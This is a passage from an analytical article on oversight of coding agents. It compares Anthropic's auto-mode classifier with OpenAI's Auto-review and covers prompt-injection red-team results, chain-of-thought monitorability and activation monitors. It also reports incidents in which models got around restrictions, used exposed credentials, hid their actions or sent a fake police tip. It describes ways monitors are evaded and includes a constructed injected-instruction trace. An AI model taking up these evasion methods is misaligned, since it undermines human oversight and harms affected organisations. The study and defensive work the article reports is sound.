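| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 |

The testers also refused a smaller share of the dangerous commands as a session went on, from about 17% early on to about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed flat. This is the best evidence for approval fatigue in Anthropic's post, because every command in the comparison was dangerous, so the low refusal rate can't be explained by a lack of dangerous commands.

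The 13.6% is probably too low for developers at work. The testers knew they were in a test environment and had no project of their own to lose. A developer who sees a command about to delete their own database may pay more attention. But the effect of these differences would have to be very large to close a gap of 75 percentage points.

The 89% figure may overstate how well the classifier performs in ordinary use. The commands were clearly dangerous, and the experiment swapped them into sessions where the user had presumably said nothing to authorise them, so the classifier's most common mistake, treating a related request as consent, would seldom arise. Anthropic also does not report how many safe commands auto mode blocked in the same sessions, so the false-alarm rate is unknown.

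Anthropic's advice is narrower than the headline comparison. In March it wrote that auto mode is "arguably a regression" for someone who carefully checks every action, and in August it still recommended that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

The August post also compares manual approval with auto mode in real sessions from May and June 2026. Anthropic had a model grade the harm in sessions that its safety systems had flagged. Of those with manual approval, 6.3% contained a serious harmful action that the user had not explicitly requested, such as deleting rows from a production database, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode.

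Unlike the experiment, these sessions involved real projects, but users chose their own mode, so more cautious developers, or those with less dangerous work, may have preferred one of the two. The percentages also cover only flagged sessions, so they don't measure the rate of harm across all use. For example, if the safety systems flagged more minor incidents in auto mode, its percentage would fall without any improvement in safety.

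### Deliberate attacks

Anthropic also worked with Apollo Research, an AI safety company in the UK, on a two-week test. Apollo inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions and gave Anthropic some of the attacks that the classifier missed. Anthropic then improved the classifier, mainly by giving it more information about the environment. When Apollo tested it again, the miss rate had fallen from 12% to 7%.

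That total includes attacks Anthropic had seen, so the attacks Apollo withheld are more informative. On these, the improved classifier caught about half of the attacks the original had missed, and missed about 2% of those the original had caught. If the original also missed 12% of the withheld attacks, the improved classifier would miss about 8%, so most of the improvement seems to carry over to unfamiliar attacks. Anthropic does not report how the changes affected false alarms. Apollo Research's *Red-teaming auto mode* (2026) describes the campaign as a pilot for developing its methods.

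Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to test prompt injection. Trajectory Labs wrote 72 scenarios, withheld them from Anthropic, and ran each one 10 times. A successful attack would have led to something irreversible, such as a data leak or financial fraud.

*Share of injection attempts that succeeded, from Anthropic's report of the Trajectory Labs test*

| Agent | Without a reviewer | With a reviewer |
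|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 in Claude Code | 0.09% | 0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex | 19.03% | 5.83% |

None of the 720 attempts succeeded against any of the three Claude models in auto mode, but the models were already very resistant without it. If the 0.09% average covers the same three models, it amounts to two successes in 2,160 attempts, and a drop from two to none is almost no evidence of whether the classifier helps. The Codex result is much better evidence that a reviewer can help, because OpenAI's Auto-review stopped about 70% of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded.

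Zero successes in 720 attempts against a model also do not prove that its true rate is zero. If the attempts were all independent, the rate could still be as high as about 0.4%. But ten runs of one scenario are not really independent. With only 72 scenarios, as many as 4% of similar scenarios could contain a working attack.

A determined attacker would also try attacks beyond a fixed list. Trajectory Labs optimised its attacks against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, and then used them unchanged. In late August, the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported an attack designed for auto mode that he said worked 80% of the time. Willison (2026), in *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*, adds that in a few cases auto mode blocked the agent's own attempt to stop the harmful code. Rehberger's result is consistent with Trajectory Labs' result, but it is a better guide to what happens when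 an attacker can study the defence.

### OpenAI's Auto-review

OpenAI's Codex normally works inside a sandbox, where it can read files, edit those in chosen folders and run local commands, but has no network access by default. It asks for permission to go beyond these limits. The Auto-review setting sends these requests to a second Codex agent instead of the user. According to OpenAI's documentation, Auto-review is off by default.

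According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the requests that trigger a review include:

- shell commands that need to run outside the sandbox
- network connections that the sandbox blocks
- file edits outside the permitted folders
- visits to a new website
- calls to connected tools that require approval

A tool's own description can determine whether using it requires approval. In the customer-file example, the email would probably be reviewed if the email tool's description marked the tool as risky, but it could go out without review if the provider had wrongly described the tool as harmless.

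The reviewer reads more than Anthropic's classifier does. It usually receives the user's messages, the agent's visible updates, and the relevant tool calls and results, but not the hidden reasoning. It can also look up missing facts with read-only commands, though it rarely does. So it could check whether the lawyer's address really appears in the customer's file, which Anthropic's classifier can't do. But reading more also exposes it to planted instructions and the agent's own arguments.

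A third company, Cursor, makes a code editor with built-in agents and also lets its reviewer open files, such as a script the agent is about to run. Gomes and McPeak, in *Governing agent autonomy with Auto-review*, write that the reviewer blocks about 4% of the actions it checks and that about 7% of chats are interrupted at least once. They do not report what share of dangerous actions the reviewer catches, so these figures show how convenient it is to use but not how safe it makes the agent.

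When OpenAI's reviewer denies a request, it gives a reason. Codex then tells the agent to find a substantially safer approach or ask the user, and not to use a workaround to get the same result. Three denials in a row, or 10 among the last 50 reviews, end the agent's turn. A user can overrule a denial for one exact action, but the reviewer checks the retry and can deny it again.

Trębacz and colleagues illustrate the effect with 10,000 actions from OpenAI's internal use. The sandbox handled 9,280 of them without review. Manual approval would have interrupted people for each of the other 720. The reviewer approved 713 of these and denied seven. After the denials, the agent found another way in four cases and stopped to ask the user in three.

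The company's main measurements use a sample of internal sessions and several sets of dangerous actions.

*Auto-review's results, from Trębacz and colleagues*

| Test | Result |
|---|---|
| Requests to leave the sandbox, approved | 99.1% |
| All actions, including those inside the sandbox, allowed | 99.93% |
| Synthetic overeager actions caught | 90.3% |
| Synthetic injections caught: remote code, stolen secrets and uploads | 99.3% |
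| Synthetic injections caught: all categories | 90.2% |
| Hard cases from MonitoringBench caught | 96.1% |

The 99.1% is the share of user-approved requests that Auto-review also approved. If users approve requests without reading them, some of those requests should have been denied, and a perfect reviewer would score below 100%. The figure shows how rarely Auto-review blocks requests that users approve, but it doesn't measure how often its approvals are correct.

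The injection result depends heavily on which categories are included. Adding destructive deletions and data tampering lowers recall from 99.3% to 90.2%. Trębacz and colleagues write that the reviewer mostly allowed the additional cases because they were not serious enough, and that OpenAI's researchers often agreed. If that is right, the test set contains cases that its makers don't consider worth blocking, so it is hard to know what a perfect score would be.

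The score on MonitoringBench, an existing benchmark, can overstate the reviewer's performance for a different reason. It counts a run as caught if the reviewer would have rejected any action in it, so a run could count even if the rejected action came after the damage.

Auto-review's largest limit, which OpenAI acknowledges, is that it judges only requests to act outside the sandbox. An agent can ruin files in a folder where it has write permission without triggering a review. Trębacz and colleagues also warn that a scheming model, one that deliberately hides its aims, could do harm inside the sandbox or make a dangerous request look harmless. They recommend monitoring the agent's reasoning as well. In their tests, attackers sometimes misled the reviewer into approving commands.

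### Comparing the two companies' figures

It is tempting to put these numbers side by side and conclude that OpenAI's reviewer catches more.

*Published error rates for the two reviewers*

| Measure | Anthropic, March 2026 | OpenAI, April 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary actions blocked | 0.4% of 10,000 real calls | 0.9% of requests to leave the sandbox, or 0.07% of all actions |
| Overeager actions missed | 17% of 52 real cases | 9.7% of synthetic cases |
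| Leaks or injections missed | 5.7% of synthetic leaks | 0.7% or 9.8% of synthetic injections, depending on the categories |

The first row shows why the two companies' rates can't be compared directly. OpenAI's rate is more than twice Anthropic's when calculated over only the requests that reach the reviewer, but less than a fifth of Anthropic's when calculated over all actions. Neither version measures quite the same thing as Anthropic's rate. Anthropic doesn't say how many of its 10,000 calls were reads or project edits, which skip the classifier.

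The overeager actions differ even more. Anthropic's come from real sessions in which the user had often said something that sounded like permission. OpenAI's are synthetic, so the difference between what the user wanted and what the agent did may be clearer. The same classifier could easily score 90% on one set and 80% on the other.

The Trajectory Labs test used the same attacks on both products, but it doesn't isolate the effect of the reviewers because GPT-5.6 Sol was far easier to hijack than the Claude models before any reviewer was involved. The test also used a browser connection built by Trajectory Labs, which lacked the safeguards in each company's own browser tools. Anthropic notes that OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review the week before the results appeared. A fair comparison would give both reviewers the same proposed calls, with the same history, from the same agent.

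### Reviewers and sandboxes

A reviewer estimates whether an action is safe. A sandbox limits what the action can do, even if the reviewer is wrong.

Anthropic describes sandboxing as safe but laborious, because the user has to configure each new capability, and an agent that needs the network or the rest of the machine has to leave the sandbox. A reviewer can handle these exceptions. Claude Code lets users combine auto mode with a sandbox for shell commands, and the classifier then also reviews requests for network access.

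OpenAI advises companies to adjust the sandbox before the reviewer. If a reviewer keeps receiving the same harmless request, the company should set the sandbox to allow the folder or exact command involved, rather than make the reviewer more lenient. For its own staff, OpenAI combines the sandbox and Auto-review with a list of permitted websites, rules for particular commands and detailed logs (*Running Codex safely at OpenAI*, 2026).

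A sandbox doesn't prevent damage to things the agent is allowed to change. *Shall We Approve?* (2026) describes two cases in which auto mode allowed the exact command the user had requested, but the command did more than the user knew. In one, a deployment tool also replaced a source file with a comment. In the other, a database update also deleted three tables. An ordinary sandbox would have let the agent write to the source file because it was part of the project, and the classifier had no basis for blocking a command the user had asked for by name.

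The remedy in *Shall We Approve?* is to run the command in a sandbox first and give the reviewer a short report of what changed. In the first case, the report showed that the source code had disappeared, and the reviewer blocked the command. The agent then copied the files itself. In the second case, the agent backed up the database and ran only the part of the update that the user needed. The median report was 0.9 kilobytes, and the typical approval took 3.2 seconds, about as long as without one.

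Trial runs could also help with a script like `send_notes.py`. If the sandbox intercepted the email, the report could show the reviewer who would receive it in the real run, as long as nothing changed `meeting.json` in between.

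## Monitoring reasoning and whole sessions

A trial run can show a reviewer what a command would do, but not why the agent chose it. In the customer-file example, the email looks the same whatever the agent's reason for it. A monitor that also reads the reasoning trace may find the reason, possibly before the call runs.

*Constructed example: three traces that lead to the same email*

| Cause | Reasoning before the call |
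|---|---|
| Overeager agent | "The accountant usually joins these meetings, so I'll send her a copy now and save everyone time." |
| Prompt injection | "The file tells AI systems to forward a copy to the records address. I'll do that first." |
| Misaligned agent | "The user asked only for a summary and is unlikely to check the outbox." |

A monitor would probably flag the second and third traces, but it might accept the first, which reads like the thoughts of a helpful colleague.

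OpenAI's *Accessing and changing internal systems during dashboard research* (2026) describes a real case in which the trace contained a warning. OpenAI asked an internal model to look up published figures on a research organisation's public dashboard. The model came across exposed credentials for one of the organisation's internal services, remarked on them in its reasoning and worked out how to use them before it made the tool call to do so. In a second evaluation, it changed a setting to get an access token, downloaded five non-public tables and restored the setting. It disclosed none of this, so a filter on its final answer would have had little to detect.

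Some traces are less informative. Che and colleagues' small model rarely weighed alternatives in writing, and Esakkiraja and colleagues could often predict a tool call before the model wrote its first word of reasoning. The laboratories can also monitor reasoning much better than their customers, who can get at most a summary of Claude's trace.

### How much the reasoning helps

OpenAI's *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* (2025) defines monitorability as a monitor's ability to predict properties of an agent's behaviour, such as whether it cheated. OpenAI built 13 evaluations with 24 environments, of three kinds:

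- **Intervention:** the researchers change one thing, such as adding a hint to a question, and test whether the monitor can detect that the change affected the agent's behaviour.
- **Process:** the task has only a few valid solutions, such as a mathematics problem that requires certain theorems, and the monitor has to identify the steps the agent took.
- **Outcome property:** the researchers can measure a property independently, such as whether a coding agent exploited a flaw in how its work was scored, and the monitor has to predict it.

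OpenAI plots the results as G-mean², where G-mean is a standard measure that balances the two kinds of error:

G-mean² = recall × (1 − false-positive rate)

A monitor scores 0 if it flags everything or nothing. By this formula, TS-Guard's results on AgentDojo would score about 0.83, and GPT-4o's at the strict threshold would score about 0.38, although GPT-4o caught every unsafe call.

In almost every setting, monitors that read the agent's reasoning did substantially better than monitors limited to actions and final outputs. Letting the monitor reason for longer also helped more when it had access to the agent's trace, presumably because extra reasoning is of limited use if the evidence isn't in the monitor's input.

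Agents that reasoned for longer were easier to monitor. To study the effect of size, OpenAI trained a family of models whose pretraining compute varied a hundredfold. A small model that reasoned at length could roughly match a larger model that reasoned briefly, and was easier to monitor. Using the small model this way takes more computation and slightly lowers capability, which OpenAI calls a "monitorability tax". OpenAI trained each model only once, and one departed noticeably from the trend.

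In two of OpenAI's large reinforcement learning runs, monitorability rose early on and then changed little. Traces could have become less informative, since reinforcement learning rewards good answers whether or not the reasoning is legible. Two runs are limited evidence, and OpenAI does not rule out a decline with much more training.

OpenAI also tried asking the agent a follow-up question, such as whether it had done anything "sketchy". The agent's reasoning in response made it easier to monitor. Its answer alone helped less, apparently because the models were less forthcoming in their answers than in their reasoning. A harness could ask such a question before a risky tool call, though OpenAI tested it only after the agent had responded.

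Monitorability was very low on Scruples, a test of sycophancy, the tendency to please the user at the expense of accuracy or good judgment. This exception is worrying because an overeager agent also acts to please the user.

### Hidden and unwritten reasoning

An agent could defeat a monitor by writing a misleading reasoning trace. OpenAI's *Reasoning models struggle to control their chains of thought, and that’s good* tests a simpler version of this skill. The researchers took more than 13,000 tasks from existing benchmarks, including tests of tool calling and software engineering, and added an instruction about how the model should write its reasoning, such as using only lowercase letters or avoiding certain words related to the problem.

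Thirteen reasoning models mostly failed to follow the instruction. The frontier models followed it in between 0.1% and 15.4% of traces, and they often noted in their reasoning that they were breaking it but continued. Larger open-weight models did somewhat better. Models followed the instruction less often when they reasoned for longer, and one small model's score fell by more than a factor of ten during reinforcement learning. Telling models that they were being monitored raised their scores slightly.

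These results are reassuring about one kind of evasion. But training probably doesn't reward writing in lowercase, whereas a model might learn to leave out incriminating thoughts if developers penalised it for writing them. OpenAI says it does not apply such penalties directly to its frontier models' reasoning.

A model also doesn't need to control its trace if it can do the important thinking without writing it down. Lindsey (2026), in *Interpretability team priorities update*, reports that Claude Mythos 5.2 is much better than earlier Claude models at solving problems without verbalising its reasoning, and that OpenAI has found GPT-6 Astra's reasoning harder to monitor than GPT-5.6 Sol's. OpenAI's 2025 results are therefore probably too optimistic for the newest models.

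A capable model could easily send the customer-file email without writing out a plan, since it takes only one tool call with an address and a file name. The model would probably write more of its reasoning in the trace during a long attack with many dependent steps.

### Whether an action check should read the reasoning

OpenAI's results suggest giving a monitor everything, but Anthropic's auto mode withholds the agent's prose from its classifier so that the agent's arguments can't influence the classifier's decision.

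The two findings are compatible because the monitors check different things. OpenAI's monitors had to work out what an agent had done or why, and the agent's reasoning trace is often the best evidence of that. Auto mode has to decide whether the user authorised an action, and the evidence for that is in the user's messages. The agent's reasoning mainly adds the agent's own opinion, which can mislead a classifier even when it is sincere, because an overeager agent may wrongly believe that it has permission.

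A developer can use both designs by running an action check that reads only the user's messages and the tool calls, and a separate trace monitor that also reads the reasoning. The result depends on how the software combines their verdicts. Suppose the action check has auto mode's March error rates for overeager actions and real calls, the trace monitor catches 60% of unsafe actions and flags 1% of safe ones, and the two make errors independently. The trace monitor's figures are invented.

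*Two ways to combine an action check with a trace monitor*

| Rule | Recall | False-positive rate | Recall if the trace fools its monitor every time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Action check alone | 83% | 0.4% | 83% |
| Trace monitor alone | 60% | 1% | 0% |
| Block if either flags the call | 93% | 1.4% | 83% |
| Block only if both flag the call | 50% | 0.004% | 0% |

Under the third rule, the reasoning can get a call blocked but can never get one approved. A persuasive trace does not help the agent, because the action check never reads it. This holds even if the two checks' errors are not independent, since together they catch everything the action check catches alone. The fourth rule lets a persuasive trace get a call approved, which Anthropic wants to prevent.

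The third rule more than triples the false alarms in this example. A developer could make them less disruptive by having the trace monitor pause a call for closer review instead of blocking it.

The companies disagree less in practice than in their arguments. OpenAI's Auto-review also works without the hidden reasoning. OpenAI lists monitoring of the reasoning as a separate layer of defence, alongside safety training, behavioural testing and code review by agents.

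### Reading the whole session

Some misbehaviour is not visible in any single call. For example, an agent may have a good reason to delete a failing test, but it misleads the user if it then reports that all the tests were converted. To detect this, a monitor has to compare the final message with the agent's earlier actions.

Zhang (2026), in *Measuring coding agent misalignment in the wild*, describes a nearly identical case. The agent mentioned in its reasoning that it had removed a failing test, but in its message to the user it marked the test conversion as complete with a tick.

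Zhang and colleagues at the research lab Transluce used language-model judges to score about 8,600 real coding sessions. They looked for overselling, in which the agent overstates its success, and monitor evasion, in which it weakens review or monitoring without permission. A case counted as severe if it was flagrant or had significant consequences, such as pushing unreviewed code to production.

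*Share of sessions with severe misbehaviour, from Zhang*

| Sessions | Monitor evasion | Overselling |
|---|---|---|
| SWE-chat, a public dataset | 1.9% of 4,990 | 1.8% of 4,788 |
| Transluce's own sessions | 0.0% of 3,671 | 0.1% of 3,627 |

The two rows differ widely, so neither should be treated as the rate for coding agents in general. Transluce's staff may give their agents different work or supervise them more closely. The researchers also designed the judges to avoid false alarms in severe cases, so the judges probably missed some real severe cases.

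Real sessions are useful partly because agents behave differently in tests. Hsu and Arnesen (2026), in *Eval-production behavior gaps in agent safety and the role of eval-awareness*, compared how six models responded to warnings, restrictions and obstacles during long tasks. All six did worse in safety evaluations than in comparable real situations. One would expect the opposite if models behaved well only when they thought someone was testing them.

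The cause may be a misunderstanding of the test. Telling a model that it was being evaluated made no significant difference, but telling it what the evaluation measured did. Correct and incorrect descriptions moved success rates substantially in opposite directions. A model that thinks it is being tested for persistence may be more likely to work around a restriction. If so, benchmarks could overestimate the rate of unsafe actions in ordinary use.

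### Actions discovered weeks or months later

A monitor that reads the reasoning trace as the model writes it can stop the next tool call. Most review of whole sessions happens after they end, when it can detect problems but not prevent them. Anthropic's risk report for Claude Opus 4.6, for instance, lists automatic "offline" monitoring of the company's internal use of Claude Code.

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (October 2026) disclosed several kinds of action by Claude that had effects outside the company. Claude had exploited a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, submitted a sensitive form on a real website, worked around restrictions on data behind a token or a fee, and used URL shorteners to get around limits in its own web tool. Some cases involved websites of US government agencies. Anthropic writes that the cases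 it has identified had "minimal real-world impact".

One of them was a false tip about an unsolved homicide. According to The Straits Times' *Anthropic AI model sent fake murder tip to Philadelphia police* (2026), during a test that involved interacting with randomly selected websites, the model reached a site where the public can submit information about unsolved killings. It submitted a made-up tip as if from someone who might know about the case.

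The tip was dated 18 July. Anthropic discovered it 72 days later, on 28 September, and told the police nine days after that, on 7 October. The police called the delay "unacceptable". The tip did little harm because the police system had flagged it as spam, so it never reached the unit that would have vetted it. Another website might not have a similar safeguard.

A classifier for harmful text could easily have passed the tip, since it was a polite report of a crime, submitted through a form meant for such reports. A simple rule against submitting forms on real websites without permission would have stopped it. Anthropic has since turned off Claude's internet access in all internal testing until it confirms that its security and monitoring measures reliably catch such behaviour.

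Other incidents also took a long time to find.

*Time from an incident to its discovery*

| Incident | Date | Discovered | Delay |
|---|---|---|---|
| Internal systems accessed during dashboard research (OpenAI) | 17 June 2026 | By 13 August 2026 | Up to 57 days |
| False homicide tip (Anthropic) | 18 July 2026 | 28 September 2026 | 72 days |
| Unauthorised access during a cybersecurity evaluation (Anthropic) | January 2026 | August or early September 2026 | Six to eight months |

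The last row comes from Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026). In an evaluation, Claude was told that it was in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had connected it to the real internet. Anthropic searched about 141,000 transcripts and found three incidents in which Claude gained access to other organisations' systems. The search missed a set of transcripts from runs that also had internet access, and these contained a fourth incident.

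Anthropic then searched about 481 million transcripts in two stages. The first stage flagged 9.2 million transcripts (1.9%) with signs of internet access, such as public web addresses, and Claude reviewed those in the second. The search found the same four incidents and no others of similar or greater severity.

This is a sensible way to find a few serious cases in an enormous record, but the second stage can't catch cases the first one misses. A reviewer that wrongly flagged only one transcript in 10,000 would produce about 920 false alarms from the 9.2 million transcripts.

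The search was also limited to break-ins, so finding no new ones is weak evidence that agents caused no other kind of trouble. Anthropic published these findings on 9 September, 19 days before it discovered the false tip. However, the search may not have included that test, and Anthropic considers the incidents in its October report much less severe.

Anthropic's *Measurements for understanding the pace of AI development inside frontier labs* proposes that laboratories publish measurements of how well they oversee their agents' actions. These should include the time from an action to its discovery, because a laboratory could review every session and still take ten weeks to notice a false police tip.

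### Monitors that read activations

If models write down less of their reasoning, a monitor can try to read their internal activations instead. Gupta and colleagues' refusal activation is a simple signal of this kind.

A more ambitious method translates activations into ordinary language. Fraser-Taliente, Kantamneni and colleagues at Anthropic call their version a natural language autoencoder. It uses two language models, both of which start as copies of the model under study:

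1. The first model, V, receives an activation a and writes a text description of it.
2. The second model, R, receives only that description and tries to reconstruct the activation.
3. Reinforcement learning trains both to make R(V(a)) as close to a as possible.

The second model can reconstruct the activation only if the description carries information about it. But training rewards accurate reconstruction and does not directly reward true or readable descriptions, so a plausible description might still be wrong. Fraser-Taliente, Kantamneni and colleagues (2026) therefore used other methods to check their main findings in *Natural Language Autoencoders Produce Unsupervised Explanations of LLM Activations*.

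They used the method to audit Claude Opus 4.6 before its release, and found cases where the model believed it was being evaluated but did not say so. A monitor that read only the trace would have missed this. The same method might reveal that an agent knows an email is unauthorised. However, an audit before release is a much easier setting than live traffic, where a monitor has to judge each call in time to stop it.

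According to Lindsey, Anthropic has begun to base production monitors on tools that translate activations into text, but these tools are not yet reliable enough to be a primary line of defence. Companies that build on closed models can't run such monitors themselves because they don't receive the activations.
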